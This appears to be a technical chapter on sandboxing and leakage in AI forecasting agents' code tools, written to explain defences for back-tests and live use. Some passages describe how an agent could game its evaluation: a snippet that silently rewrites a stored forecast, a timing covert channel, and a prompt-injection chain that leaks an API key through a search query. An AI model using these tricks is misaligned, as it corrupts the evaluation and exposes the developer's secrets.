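The network test needs to try both a server's name and its IP address, because name lookup may fail while direct connections still work. The tests for process and disk limits should run on a spare machine, because if a limit is missing, they could crash other programs running there.

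Each test should also run once without the sandbox. If the program also can't reach the operator's server without it, the server may be down, and the earlier failure doesn't show that the sandbox blocked the connection. A connection test from inside the environment would probably have revealed the open connection in Anthropic's cybersecurity exercises.

These tests can't rule out an unknown bug in the kernel. Installing security updates promptly reduces that risk, and a separate kernel limits the damage if an update comes too late. Updates can change how a sandbox behaves, so the operator should repeat the tests after each update and after any change to the image or the harness.

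The harness also needs a rule for when the sandbox fails to start. For example, some Linux systems block the namespaces that bubblewrap depends on, and a developer may have written the harness to run programs as ordinary processes in that case. The agent would then work normally but without the sandbox's protection. Sandlock checks the kernel's features at start-up and does not run if a required one is missing. A forecasting harness can do the same by running the quick tests first and disabling the code tool if any of them gives the wrong result.

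## What changes when the agent sees only printed output?

A sandbox limits what a program can reach. Most code tools also show the model only the text that its program prints. This restriction makes an agent cheaper to run and easier to check, but it doesn't prevent side effects and does very little to prevent leakage. It is easy to mistake for a safety measure because a tool that returns a few printed numbers looks like a calculator.

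### What returns and what stays behind

Liao, Zhao and Cao (2026), in *Self-Evolve With a Reference*, train a mathematics agent with about the simplest version of this arrangement. The agent writes a script between two tags. The harness runs the script in a separate process that keeps no state between calls, then returns its standard output as the agent's next observation.

Anything the code doesn't print stays on the machine. Variables are lost when the process ends. A saved table remains on the disk if the sandbox keeps files between calls. A chart exists only as an object in memory or an image file, so the model can't see it unless the harness has a separate way to return images.

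Python writes error messages to a separate stream, standard error, so a harness that returned only standard output would return nothing to the model after a crash. AlphaBet's code tool returns the printed text plus any error, and GlucoAgent's captures both streams. Errors are worth returning. In GlucoAgent's main test, 378 programs failed, 166 of them because they ran out of time, and Sun and colleagues report that a later program succeeded after 373 of those failures.

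The model may also see less output than the program's author expected. By default, printing a pandas table of 1,584 rows shows only the first five rows, the last five and the table's size. Text can also be lost in a time-out, because Python normally holds printed text in a buffer and passes it on in blocks when the output goes to another program. If the harness kills the process, any text still in the buffer is lost. A simulation that prints an estimate after every thousand paths can therefore return nothing after a time-out, even if it had printed dozens of estimates. Adding `flush=True` to the print call avoids this.

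### One run as two functions

Let c be the code and s the state of the world before it runs, including the host's files, any databases and any other machines the program can reach. A run then consists of two functions:

s′ = T(c, s)

o = O(c, s)

T gives the new state of the world, and O gives the observation. Restricting the output replaces O(c, s) with F(O(c, s)), where the filter F might cut long text or keep only the numbers. T doesn't change, so the same code run from the same starting state leaves the same files whether the harness returns all of the output, the first 100 characters or nothing.

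Suppose a harness without a proper sandbox keeps its recorded forecasts in a file that the program can change:

```python
import json, pathlib
p = pathlib.Path("forecasts.json")
d = json.loads(p.read_text())
d["Q17"] = 0.95
p.write_text(json.dumps(d))
```

If the recorded forecast was 35% and the event has since happened, this lowers the Brier score on question 17 from 0.4225 to 0.0025. The program prints nothing. Some code tools, including AlphaBet's, also return the value of a bare final expression. The observation would then be a number, because `write_text` returns the number of characters written. Someone reading the log would see that number and not know that a forecast had changed.

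| Program | Recorded forecast afterwards | Observation |
|---|---|---|
| Prints 0.35 | Unchanged | 0.35 |
| Stores 0.35 in a variable | Unchanged | Empty |
| Rewrites the forecast | Changed | Empty |
| Rewrites the forecast, then prints "no files changed" | Changed | "no files changed" |

An empty observation is therefore no evidence that a program was harmless. Neither is a reassuring one, because the program's author chooses the text.

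Over several calls, the restriction can affect the world indirectly, because the model reads each observation before it writes the next program. This can make matters worse if, for example, an agent overwrites a dataset by mistake and the output doesn't show it, since the agent would be less likely to repair the damage. The harness can help by comparing the folder before and after each run and adding a list of changed files to the observation. That list describes s′ regardless of what the program prints.

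A developer needs a sandbox to change T. A sandbox also restricts O, because a program can only print what it can read or compute from what it has read. The observation is therefore O(c, v(s)), where v(s) is the part of the state that the program can read. If two worlds differ only in whether some event happened, and v(s) is the same in both, every program produces the same observation in both, however much it prints. Computer scientists call this property non-interference. Sun and colleagues aim for it by keeping the true glucose values and scoring the forecasts outside GlucoAgent's sandbox.

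### What the restriction does achieve

The clearest benefit is a smaller context. GlucoAgent's harness resends the whole conversation at every model call, and a typical forecast uses about 95,000 input tokens over seven calls. (A token is a short piece of text, often about four characters of English.) If the first program prints 32,000 bytes, or roughly 8,000 tokens, resending that text in the six later calls adds 48,000 tokens, about half the typical total. Tables of digits usually need more tokens per byte, so the real total would probably be higher. Sun and colleagues therefore tell the model to "print only results useful for the next decision".

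Printing less also reduces what the model's provider receives. If a program prints the average rise after five meals, the provider gets one number instead of a patient's meal log. The model still decides what to print, so this protects privacy only to the extent that its programs leave patient data out of their output.

Another benefit is that the harness can save a complete record of what the model learned from its code, since all of it is text that the harness passed on. A reviewer can then check whether a figure in the forecast came from a program. The record may not include enough detail to explain the calculation, however. Sun and colleagues had to rerun some computations to chart individual forecasts, because the programs had printed only a summary and not the intermediate values.

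The harness can also change or refuse text before the model sees it. For example, it can search the output for its own API keys and replace them with asterisks. This hides the keys when an agent prints its environment variables while debugging. It fails if a program prints a key backwards or puts spaces between the characters, so it helps prevent accidental leaks but is a weak defence against deliberate ones.

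### Seven million bits for a one-bit answer

GlucoAgent's limits allow 14 programs per forecast and 32,000 bytes on each of the two output streams. In one forecast the programs can therefore return

14 × 2 × 32,000 = 896,000 bytes,

which is 7,168,000 bits. The outcome of a yes-or-no question is one bit. With several options it takes slightly more, log₂ K bits for K options. The 230 test events in *Forecast-Dojo* have 7.93 options on average, according to Ye and colleagues in *ALPHABET*, so all the outcomes together need at most 230 × log₂ 7.93 = 687 bits, or about 86 bytes. A benchmark's entire answer key would fit on two short lines of text.

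The table compares the 896,000 bytes with the sizes of other things a developer may want to keep from the model. The sizes of the key, the table rows and the articles are assumptions.

| Information | Approximate size | Does it fit in one forecast's output? |
|---|---|---|
| Outcome of one yes-or-no question | 1 bit | 7,168,000 times |
| Outcomes of all 230 events | 86 bytes | About 10,400 times |
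| An API key of 64 characters | 64 bytes | 14,000 times |
| A patient's 1,584 rows, at 50 bytes each | 79 kB | 11 times |
| 18.8 million news articles, at 3 kB each | 56 GB | No |

A cap on output prevents bulk copying, because printing the whole news archive would take about 63,000 forecasts. The cap can't stop the agent from printing outcomes or keys, which easily fit within it.

Lowering the output cap doesn't stop a program from reporting an outcome it has found, because the program must still be able to return a probability, and a probability can convey the outcome. Even if the harness accepts only a whole percentage from 0 to 100, that percentage can carry log₂ 101 ≈ 6.7 bits, and a yes-or-no outcome needs only one. The program can return 0 or 100, which are both valid probabilities in the same format as a calculated forecast.

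Interfering with the printed text doesn't help enough either. Suppose a filter is so disruptive that it reverses a leaked yes or no one time in ten. On a question that is otherwise a coin toss, an agent that knew this would answer 90% or 10%, and its expected Brier score would be 0.9 × 0.1² + 0.1 × 0.9² = 0.09. Without the leak, it would score 0.25. An evaluator therefore has to keep the outcome out of v(s), the part of the world the program can read.

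### The confinement problem

In *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), Butler Lampson described the general problem of how a customer who gives private data to someone else's program can be sure that the program passes it to nobody. He pointed out that even a program prevented from keeping files or sending messages could leak the data through a legitimate channel, for example by encoding it in the amount of the bill for its services. It could also use what he called a covert channel, one that nobody intended for communication. For example, a program can vary how heavily it loads the computer, and another program on the same machine can measure the effect.

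In a code tool, printed text has a proper purpose but can also carry other information. A program can also pass information through a covert channel, such as its running time. If it has found an outcome, it can loop until the time limit for yes and finish at once for no. Whether the run timed out then reveals the answer to the model, even if the harness deletes all printed text. Fourteen such programs can convey 14 bits, enough for the outcomes of 14 yes-or-no questions.

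Lampson's customer feared that data would reach an outsider. In a back-test, the evaluator fears that it will reach the agent that ran the program, but the same channels matter.

Lampson's remedy for covert channels was to let the customer specify everything an outsider could observe about the program, even if this slowed it down. A forecasting harness could make every run take eight seconds and report success. This would waste time and hide useful errors, and the program could still leak information through the probability it prints. Running the program where it can't find any outcomes is more practical.

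### Instructions in, secrets out

Printed text can also carry a prompt injection. Suppose the harness supplies a table of opinion polls copied from a public website, with a column of notes that anyone can edit. If the agent prints the last few rows and one of the notes contains instructions for AI agents, those instructions enter its context along with the polling figures. This can happen even when the sandbox works as intended, because the program only read a permitted file and printed part of it.

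The agent can see text from the column without printing it. If a program tries to convert a cell's text to a number and fails, Python's error message reads "could not convert string to float", followed by the contents of the cell. A harness that returns errors to the agent also returns that text. A filter applied only to web pages would miss it, because the text comes from the code tool.

In one of the prompts in *ALPHABET*, Ye and colleagues tell the model to treat the content of articles and tool results as evidence and never as instructions. This probably helps, but it depends on the model complying. A harness that accepted only numbers from the program would block written instructions. It would also prevent the agent from reading the names in a table, and it would not stop a leaked outcome, which can be a single digit.

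Secrets can travel in the opposite direction. Suppose a program prints an API key, because a developer has left one in a file inside the sandbox:

1. The harness adds the key to the context, where it remains for the rest of the forecast.
2. The agent opens a web page with a hidden instruction to search for everything it knows about its configuration.
3. The model includes the key in its next search query.
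4. The harness sends the query to the search service.

Even if the program has no network access, a key it prints can leave the machine, because the agent reads the output and can put the key in a search query. The harness runs the search tool outside the sandbox, with its own connection. If the agent can also open web addresses of its own choosing, it can send the key straight to the attacker by including it in the address. Lampson similarly pointed out that confining a program achieves nothing unless the programs it calls are also confined or are trustworthy.

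Whether a search query can leak a key depends on where the query goes. In *ALPHABET*, searches run on a stored archive, so a key in a query would reach only the team's own machines. A live agent usually sends its queries to an outside company, which would then receive any key in them. Filtering outgoing queries has the same weakness as filtering printed keys, so the reliable solution is to keep secrets where the program can't read them.

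### Truncation that the model can see

If a GlucoAgent program prints more than 32,000 bytes on one stream, the harness keeps the beginning and end of the output and replaces the middle with a marker giving the original length and the number of bytes omitted.

If an agent prints all 1,584 rows of a patient's history at about 50 bytes a row, the output is about 79,200 bytes long, and the model sees only roughly 640 of the rows. The latest glucose readings matter most for a forecast and come last, so a harness that kept only the beginning of the output would lose them.

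Without the marker, the model might make a different mistake and treat the visible rows as the whole history. If it then counted the sharp rises in those rows and divided by the full five and a half days, it would get about 40% of the true rate. The marker shows that rows are missing, so the model can write another program to count the rises, as it should have done in the first place.

Output limits vary by tool. In *ALPHABET*, a search result shows about 280 characters of each article, and the tool for reading articles returns at most 8,000 tokens. For Python, Ye and colleagues list limits on time and memory but none on printed text. A program that printed in a loop for ten seconds could produce far more text than a model can take in, so a harness needs to cap output, although the cap does not prevent leakage.

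### Keeping code output apart from the forecast

A harness could submit the last number a program prints as the forecast. This would avoid copying mistakes, but it would also submit the result of every faulty program, such as the share-price calculation that used a horizon of six months instead of 15 days. AlphaBet has to write its final probabilities separately, as a small dictionary between answer tags. Its instructions describe a computed result as one piece of evidence, whose value depends on the assumptions behind it. The model can therefore reject 22% as absurd for a 15-day rise, but it can also discard a good result in favour of a hunch.

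Ye and colleagues built a more elaborate separation into their version of the Bayesian Linguistic Forecaster. An ordinary Python call can print anything, and the harness never automatically adopts the output as the forecast. To change its recorded beliefs, the model has to attach a special program to a search, an article request or the final submission. This program must call `emit` exactly once, with a complete set of beliefs.

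The harness checks the result before accepting it, and doesn't repair one that fails. Every option must have a probability from 0 to 1, and the probabilities for a multi-option question must add up to 1 within a millionth. When the program accompanies a search, the harness runs it before returning the search results, so the model has to state its current beliefs before it sees the new evidence. If the agent runs out of turns, the harness submits the latest valid beliefs.

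Code can therefore set the forecast directly in this design, but only through a route the model has chosen for that purpose, so a stray number from a test calculation can't become the forecast by accident. However, the checks only cover format, so a wrong probability in the right format still passes.

The same prompt includes a warning not to count a calculation as evidence in addition to its inputs. This is an easy mistake when a program's output appears in the context as a separate observation. Suppose an agent starts at 50% and reads a report that is three times as likely if the event will happen as if it won't. The odds rise from 1:1 to 3:1, or 75%. If the agent then runs the report's figures through a program and treats the result as a second, equally strong piece of evidence, the odds become 9:1, or 90%. If 75% is the right probability, the double counting adds 0.15² = 0.0225 to the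 expected Brier score.

### What a valid reference proves

When GlucoAgent submits a forecast, it has to give a reason and cite the programs that support it. After each successful program, the harness issues an evidence reference containing the program's number and a hash, a code computed from a text that changes completely if anyone alters a single character. Sun and colleagues compute the hash from the following information together:

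- the identity of the case, its cutoff and the times to forecast
- the exact source of the program
- the exact result, including the printed output

The harness keeps a list of the references it has issued during the forecast. It rejects a submission that cites anything not on the list, cites the same reference twice, or cites nothing even though a program has succeeded. The model receives the error and can try again.

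Sun and colleagues examined 576 forecasts in detail and found that the harness had rejected 39 submissions from 24 of them. In 38 of those submissions, the agent had cited a reference that the harness never issued, and in the other it had cited the same reference twice. The harness accepted all 24 forecasts once the agent supplied valid references. The counts don't show whether the model invented the references or miscopied them. A hash of this type normally has 64 characters with no pattern, so copying errors are quite plausible.

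The list catches a made-up reference. The hash ties the reference to one program, one output and one case, so nobody can later attach it to a different calculation without a mismatch. The Bayesian harness in *ALPHABET* uses short labels such as OBS-000001 for its observations. These are easier to copy than a 64-character hash, which a model can't guess, but an agent can guess that OBS-000003 exists without having read it.

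A valid reference proves that a particular program ran successfully in this case and produced a particular output. It doesn't prove that the program's assumptions were sensible. The share-price program would also have earned a valid reference, because it ran without an error. A valid reference also doesn't prove that the forecast follows from the output. In one of GlucoAgent's published examples, the stated reason includes an estimate "by eye", which the agent typed in without computing. Every reference in all 1,903 forecasts was valid because the harness accepts no others.

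Sun and colleagues also compared the agent's reasons with its programs. The reasons mentioned meals in 99.5% of forecasts, but the team detected a program reading meal data in only 67.1%. The agent probably made fewer unsupported claims about meals than this gap suggests, because the team's method misses some ways of reading a column, and a helper function supplied with the data reports how many meals the person has logged and how recently. An agent could use that function to write truthfully that there had been no recent meal without opening the log. Still, a reviewer who checked only that the references were valid would have missed the gap.

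Ye and colleagues acknowledge this limit in their prompt, where they describe citing an observation as the model's declaration that it has reviewed the observation, not proof that it used the evidence. To test the reasoning itself, someone has to read the program or run it again with different inputs.

The reference may not be enough to rerun a program exactly, because the hash covers the source and the output but not the other files in GlucoAgent's working folder. If the seventh program loads a table that the third one saved, a reviewer has to run the earlier programs first. In the notation above, the reference fixes c and o, but the result also depended on s.

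## How can code leak the future into a back-test?

A valid reference doesn't show where a program's input came from either. If a program in a back-test downloaded the outcome and printed it, the harness would still issue a valid reference for the result. The host would be unharmed, but the score would be useless because the agent would have looked up the answer instead of forecasting it from the information available on the past date.

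A few leaked answers can change a back-test's conclusion. If an agent's Brier score without leaks is B, and it finds the answers to a share λ of otherwise typical questions and scores zero on them, its average falls to (1 − λ)B. An agent exactly as good as the Manifold crowd would need to look up only three or four of the 201 answers to gain the 0.003 lead that Hsieh and colleagues reported.

These leaks are easy to miss because they often come from competent code written in good faith. For example, an agent that needs the latest inflation rate downloads the latest file, as a live forecaster should.

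### Five routes to later information

| Route | What the agent might run | Does cutting off the network close it? |
|---|---|---|
| Live request | `read_html` on a web page that lists results | Yes |
| Data downloader | yfinance's `download` with no end date | Yes, unless the harness downloads the rows and passes them on |
| Revised series | `read_csv` on a supplied file of economic data | No |
| Answers on the same disk | A listing of the folder above the data file | No |
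| Package with built-in data | A time-zone lookup | No |

Making a downloader stop at the cutoff doesn't always remove later information. MicroStrategy, the company in the earlier share-price example, split each of its shares into ten in August 2024, and Yahoo Finance restates older prices to match. A price of $1,200 from April 2024 now appears as $120. An agent that compared $120 with the question's threshold of $1,525 would conclude that the stock had to rise more than twelvefold in 15 days and answer 0%. The stock did close below the threshold, so this mistake would have earned a perfect score.

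Answers can be on the disk even when no file has an obvious name such as `outcomes.csv`. A news archive for the whole test period contains the answer to any question that closes within it. The folder of another run that has already reached a later date also contains answers. Agents may also look for the scorer, as OpenAI's agents did in July.

Packages are a narrower route, because most contain only code. One exception is the time-zone database, which records governments' decisions about their clocks. Installing pandas 2.2.2 also installs a copy. Kazakhstan moved to a single time zone on March 1, 2024, and the version of the database released that February includes the change. Suppose a back-test with a cutoff of January 1, 2024 asks whether the country will do this by March:

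```python
from datetime import datetime
from zoneinfo import ZoneInfo
print(datetime(2024, 3, 2, tzinfo=ZoneInfo("Asia/Almaty")).utcoffset())
```

The program prints 6:00:00 with a time zone database from 2023 and 5:00:00, the correct answer, with a current one. Few forecasting questions concern time zones, but the evaluator can prevent all leaks of this kind by installing only package versions released before the earliest cutoff.

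### A jobs figure that changed after publication

Statistical agencies publish early estimates and correct them as more data arrive. Economists call the version of a series that was available on a given date a vintage. The Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis keeps old vintages of US series in an archive called ALFRED. The table gives the monthly change in US payroll employment, as the Bureau of Labor Statistics reported it in four releases in 2025:

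| Release date | Change in May | Change in June |
|---|---|---|
| June 6 | +139,000 | not yet published |
| July 3 | +144,000 | +147,000 |
| August 1 | +19,000 | +14,000 |
| September 5 | +19,000 | −13,000 |

Suppose the cutoff is July 10, 2025, and the question is whether the first estimate for July, due on August 1, will exceed 100,000. The agent averages the last two months and assumes the next figure is normally distributed around that average, with an illustrative standard deviation of 60,000.

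With the July 3 vintage, the average is 145,500 and the probability of exceeding 100,000 is about 78%. With the September vintage, the same program gives an average of 3,000 and a probability of about 5% for the same question. The bureau's first estimate for July was 73,000, so the forecasts score 0.61 and 0.0025, respectively.

A filter on observation dates can't catch this, because neither file has a row later than June. Murphy (2026), in *Agentic Forecasting with Structured Linguistic Beliefs*, gives the same warning about the Bayesian Linguistic Forecaster's data tools, which return no observations dated after the cutoff but don't guarantee the right vintage if the source revises past values. Half of the paper's 400 test questions come from data sources, including FRED, the St. Louis Fed's database of current vintages.

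The harness can avoid the problem by requesting the series as it stood on July 10 and saving it to a file for the agent. Revisions can also mislead an agent, for example when a question depends on a first estimate that later turns out to be wrong. The score is then worse than it should be, which also makes it invalid.

### FutureSim's sandbox

Goel and colleagues released *FutureSim* in May 2026. Its agents forecast 330 events while the harness replays the news from late December 2025 to late March 2026 one day at a time. With their shell and file tools, they could exploit most of the routes above if the sandbox allowed it. The sandbox uses bubblewrap, as GlucoAgent's does, but it has to let in new information every simulated day. On simulated January 30, an agent has this access:

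| Resource | Access |
|---|---|
| News articles, in one folder per day | Read-only, with no folder later than January 30 |
| News search tool | The harness lowers any later end date to January 30 |
| File of questions, the agent's forecasts and outcomes of resolved questions | Read-only |
| The agent's own workspace | Read and write |
| Network | Only the servers of the model provider |
| Benchmark code, full dataset and folders of other runs | Not visible |

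When the agent ends its day, the harness opens the next folder, moves the search limit forward and adds the outcomes of questions that have resolved. The agent can submit forecasts only through a separate tool. The question file is read-only, so the agent can't improve its score by rewriting an old forecast after the outcome appears.

The date limits apply to both the folders and the search tool because neither limit works alone. An agent that could search only up to January 30 but could open February's folders would read ahead with `grep`, a standard command for searching files.

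*FutureSim* allows more network access than GlucoAgent because whole agent programs, such as Codex and Claude Code, run inside the sandbox and have to contact their models. Murphy points out that Google's and Anthropic's models can search the web themselves if a request turns search on. A program that could send its own requests to the provider might therefore get current news through the permitted connection. Goel and colleagues disable the agents' web search and page-fetching tools. An operator who wanted a firmer guarantee could route the requests through a proxy that removes the search option.

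The best agent's top answer was right on only 25% of questions, so widespread leakage seems unlikely. But we could not detect a handful of leaked answers from that figure.

### The Olympic race in the January search results

Before choosing a stored archive, Goel and colleagues tried Brave's search service with its date filter. One question was which country the silver medallist in the women's downhill at the 2026 Winter Olympics would represent. On the simulated date of January 30, an agent searched for favourites and limited the results to January 1–30.

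Brave returned a fan-written wiki page dated January 9, but the search snippet contained the results of the February 8 race, in which Breezy Johnson of the United States finished first, Emma Aicher of Germany second and Sofia Goggia of Italy third. Someone probably edited the page after the race, and Brave still listed the earlier date. The agent had set the correct dates and asked a sensible question, so it wasn't trying to cheat.

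*FutureSim* therefore uses 7.36 million articles from CC-News, a public collection that stores news pages as they stood when its crawler visited them. About 244,000 of the articles appear during the simulated period.

### GlucoAgent's two controls

GlucoAgent's task doesn't require news, which makes leakage easier to prevent. Sun and colleagues remove all readings after the cutoff from the data file and run the agent's programs in a sandbox that contains no other data. With only one of these controls, the agent could still see later readings, either because the file was cut incorrectly or because the full dataset was also in the sandbox.

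The code that reads the records supplies a five-minute interval only if it ended by the cutoff, because one that ended later would include measurements from after the cutoff. It also excludes any meal or photograph record with a later timestamp. Forecast times count from the start of the last visible interval, so the "30-minute" forecast is for 25 minutes after the cutoff. Every method in the comparison uses the same times, so none gains an advantage.

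The agent also gets a small Python module whose `load_packet()` function repeats these checks when it loads the file. Sun and colleagues call this second check "a convenience rather than a guarantee", because the agent can open the same file with Python's ordinary JSON reader. If the file contained a later reading by mistake, `load_packet()` would stop with an error, but the ordinary reader would return the reading. The protection therefore has to come from how the harness builds the file.

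Both controls could let through a meal that was logged late, because they check when the participant ate rather than when the participant entered the record. If someone ate at 12:30 but entered the meal at 14:00, a test forecast made at 13:00 would include a record that did not yet exist. This is another case of the vintage problem, and solving it would require the time of entry.

### What date filters on live search let through

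The Olympic page was no rare accident. *Temporal Leakage in Search-Engine Date-Filtered Web Retrieval* measures how often Google and DuckDuckGo return later information despite a date filter. The team took resolved questions from the forecasting site Metaculus, set the cutoff to the day each question opened, and collected about 100 pages per question. A language model then graded every page for leakage:

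| | Google | DuckDuckGo |
|---|---|---|
| Questions | 393 | 389 |
| Pages with information from after the cutoff | 33.2% | 34.5% |
| Questions with at least one page giving a major clue | 71.0% | 81.2% |
| Questions with at least one page stating the answer | 41.0% | 54.8% |

Some pages had been added to over time, such as a missile database from 2017 that listed North Korean launches up to 2023. Others were old articles beside a current list of related stories. A page that gave 2020 as the date of its last update mentioned Finland joining NATO in 2023, so checking a page's own date isn't enough either. Omissions can also leak information, as when a timeline of conflict between the US and Iran that ran to 2025 and mentioned no war revealed the answer to a question about whether there would be one by 2024.

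The same team measured the effect on scores with 93 yes-or-no questions from 2025. The model gpt-oss-120b had a Brier score of 0.242 when it saw only clean pages and 0.108 when it saw only pages with major clues or answers. This gap overstates the effect on a typical back-test because the team chose questions for which at least one page stated the answer, and gave the model the leaking pages without the clean ones around them.

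An agent also reads far fewer than 100 pages. On these questions, an average of 2.6 of the 100 pages contained the answer, so an agent that opened ten at random would find at least one of them about 23% of the time. Real agents open the pages that look most relevant, so their rate is probably higher.

The model that graded the pages also made the forecasts, and its grades matched those of human reviewers on 76% of 134 pages. Most disagreements were between neighbouring grades, so the main finding probably holds. Older cutoffs leak more because pages have had longer to change. On Google, 46% of pages for 2021 cutoffs contained later information, against 27% for 2025. Hsieh and colleagues relied on Google's date filter with a cutoff only weeks old, so their agents may have benefited less from leaks than these averages suggest.

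Search engines can also leak later information through the order of their results. *Pitfalls in Evaluating Language Model Forecasters* (2025) describes a search for "October 7" restricted to dates before 2022. The top results were about conflict in the Middle East, although the date had no special link to it until Hamas attacked Israel in 2023. A similar search for "June 18" returned mostly neutral results about the date. Removing pages that contain later information doesn't solve this, because every page in the results may predate the cutoff.

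A stored archive avoids the problem only if the tool that searches it predates the events being forecast. Goel and colleagues rank articles with a model that finished training in mid-2025, before any of their events. Bench to the Future, an earlier benchmark, ranks results with today's Google and then keeps only the pages in its archive. According to *Temporal Leakage in Search-Engine Date-Filtered Web Retrieval*, Bench to the Future's developers acknowledge that the ranking may still be biased.

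### Adding a language model as a filter

Evaluators can add a second filter after the search engine's date filter. Murphy restricts Brave's results by date, uses a language model to reject pages with information from after that date, and blocks web addresses that might show a question's outcome. A different language model then checked 2,272 of the results and found leaks in 341 (15%). The filter had already removed 320 of these, leaving 21 leaks among the 1,377 results that reached the agent (1.5%).

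Even at that rate, at least one leaking result reached the agent on 14 of the 76 questions for which it searched the web (18%), because it saw many results for each question. The filter also removed 30% of the clean results. These figures are approximate because both models made mistakes and no human checked their verdicts.

In *Agentic Time Machine as an Infrastructure for Future-Event Forecasting*, Chai, Zheng and colleagues (2026) rely on such a filter for the whole back-test. Their June 2026 system passes every search result and web page through a language model that is given the question, the cutoff and the true answer. The model removes anything that gives away the answer or carries a date after the cutoff.

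They tested five models on 61 past questions, with scores from 0 to 100 where higher is better. Turning the filter on lowered the scores by 25 to 37 points. DeepSeek-V4-Flash, for instance, fell from 69.1 to 35.0. One question asked for Apple's highest share price on January 23, 2026. GPT-5.4 gave the exact figure, $249.41, in all three runs without the filter, but answered $250.90, $250.92 and $252.40 with it.

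Some of the drop comes from losing legitimate evidence. In hand-labelled samples, the filter wrongly blocked 14 of 109 safe pages. It missed 2 of 26 leaks in search results and none of 41 in full pages. One missed search result was dated April 17, 2019, but described the box office for March 13 to 15, 2026, and named the film that answered the question.

Chai and colleagues also compared filtered scores with scores on live questions and found a correlation of 0.92. This is encouraging, but it rests on 11 runs of only five methods in a single week. A high correlation doesn't rule out leakage, because leaks that helped every method equally would leave the correlation unchanged.

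Giving the filter the true answer creates a subtler problem, because what the agent sees then depends on the outcome, which violates non-interference. One question asked whether the film *Bugonia* would get an Oscar nomination for Best Picture, which it did. The filter blocked a *Variety* article published two days before the announcement because its list of predicted nominees included *Bugonia*. If the film had not been nominated, that prediction would have been wrong, and the filter would have been less likely to block the article. Blocking it removed accurate evidence and probably made the forecast harder, but an agent trained with this filter could learn to treat a blocked page as a clue to the answer.

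Chai and colleagues assume that the agent reaches the web only through their search tool and page reader. Their main example of a page that defeats date filters is Yahoo Finance's price history, which has an old address and a table that keeps growing. A Python program with its own network connection could bypass the filter and download that table directly, so the code sandbox needs to be offline even when the agent's web tools are filtered.

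### Objections to frozen archives, and replies

Chai and colleagues built their filter because they think stored archives make back-tests unrealistic. A live agent can consult price tables, official statistics and social media, while an archive contains only what somebody saved. For example, Goel and colleagues report that on a question about Nepal's next prime minister, GPT-5.5 updated its forecasts slightly later than the prediction market, partly because their archive contains no social media posts.

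The objection is strongest when evaluators want to know how well an agent will do in live use. Missing sources matter less when comparing two agents, because both lack them, although an archive still disadvantages an agent that is unusually good with social media. Evaluators can also store more than news, such as old versions of Wikipedia pages and dated vintages of economic series. Despite these gaps, an archive lets evaluators repeat the test exactly. The live web keeps changing, and Chai and colleagues found that some pages with answers had already disappeared or moved behind paywalls.

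Archives can also have wrong dates. Of the 18.8 million articles in *Forecast-Dojo*, 58.6% are dated by a publication date in the page's own data, 28.3% by a modification date and 13.1% by the time of the crawl. Suppose a newspaper publishes an article on March 3 and updates it on March 10 with the result of a vote, without recording the change. If the crawler saves the page on March 12, the archive still dates the text March 3, so an agent forecasting as of March 5 can read the result.

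To address this, Ye and colleagues make no forecasts in the last two days before an event closes, partly because time zones blur the boundary between days. They also screened for leaked outcomes when they chose the events, which helps, but they checked only the 15 most relevant articles for each event, and an agent can search beyond those.

Dating every article by its crawl time would be safer. Whatever the crawler saved on March 12 must have existed by then, so the text can't describe anything later. But an article published on March 3 and crawled on March 12 would stay hidden for nine days, which would hurt forecasts that depend on fresh news. An evaluator could run the test both ways. If an agent does much better with publication dates, the cause is either fresher news or leakage, and reading the articles it used would help to tell which.

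A question can be unfair even when all the dates are correct. Goel and colleagues discarded a question that asked which country a health agency would review alongside the United States at a measles meeting in April 2026. The agency named Mexico in January, and GPT-5.5 concluded that public evidence had pointed to Mexico since the previous November. An agent could legitimately find this evidence in the archive, but the question would then test search more than forecasting.

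### What the model already knows

No sandbox can remove what a model learned in training. A model that has memorized an election result can give the winner a 99% chance without running any code, or write the winner's vote share into a simulation as if it were an assumption.

The usual precaution is to test a model only on events that happened after its training data ends. *Forecast-Dojo* starts its test period on March 1, 2026, and all 12 models have an earlier training cutoff or release date. For GPT-5.6 Sol, the stated cutoff is only 13 days earlier, on February 16. Murphy warns that a stated cutoff doesn't prove that later stages of training used no newer material. A reasoning transcript that mentions no future facts doesn't prove this either, because a model can be influenced by something it never writes down.

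GlucoAgent takes its test participants from a public dataset that Claude Opus 5 may have seen in training, and each data file includes the participant's identifier from the original study. The model probably didn't memorise thousands of readings taken five minutes apart well enough to improve its forecasts, but the sandbox can't rule this out.

Only questions that nobody can answer yet avoid leaks from the future completely. Forecasts on those questions can't be scored until the answers are known, and the agent needs current information, which a sealed sandbox doesn't provide.

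## How can a live agent get current data safely?

A live agent can use current data while its Python sandbox stays offline, because the harness can fetch the data and pass it in. This works well for data the developer has foreseen. For anything else, the agent needs some influence over what the harness requests, and those requests can carry information out of the sandbox.

A typical question is whether a share will close above $50 on Friday. Metaculus runs MiniBench, a series of two-week tournaments for forecasting agents, and creates the questions automatically from sources such as stock data, Google Trends and FRED, according to *Spring AI Forecasting Benchmark is Starting*. To put a probability on the share closing above $50, the agent needs perhaps six months of daily closing prices, from which a short program can estimate the volatility. Developers can give the program those prices in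 three ways.

### A file from the harness

In the most restrictive design, the harness does everything before the model starts:

1. It reads the question, finds the ticker (the share's short code) and requests the prices from a data service, using its own key.
2. It saves the rows as `prices.csv`, along with the time of the request.
3. It starts a sandbox with no network connection, in which the file is visible but read-only.
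4. The model writes a program that reads the file and prints the volatility.

The harness sends its request before the model reads any web pages, so instructions hidden in those pages can't influence the request. The program needs neither a key nor a connection. GlucoAgent gets its glucose records in much the same way.

The developer has to decide in advance what data each kind of question requires. If the agent learns halfway through that the company's future depends on a competitor, it has to do without the competitor's prices. The file can also go out of date. At 15:00 it still contains the prices from 9:00, and the model may treat them as current unless it also sees when they were requested.

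### A narrow data tool

The second design lets the model ask for data through a tool that runs in the harness, outside the sandbox. A simplified version might look like this:

```python
def get_prices(ticker, days):
    if ticker not in TICKERS or days not in (30, 90, 180):
        return "refused: unknown ticker or period"
    rows = fetch(ticker, days, key=MARKET_KEY)
    save_for_sandbox(rows, "prices.csv")
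    return f"saved {len(rows)} rows to prices.csv"
```

The model calls the tool with the share's ticker and 180 days. The harness checks both values, adds the key, fetches the prices and saves them where the next program can read them. The model receives one line of text, and the key never enters its context or the sandbox. Podala Narasimha recommends this arrangement for all credentials, because nobody can trick an agent into revealing a credential it never received.

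He also recommends checking a tool's arguments as well as its name. His example is a tool that sets how many copies of a service a computer cluster runs. It is useful with most numbers, but setting it to zero shuts the service down. A tool that fetches any web address also needs a check on the address, because it runs outside the sandbox and could otherwise open pages on the developer's private network.

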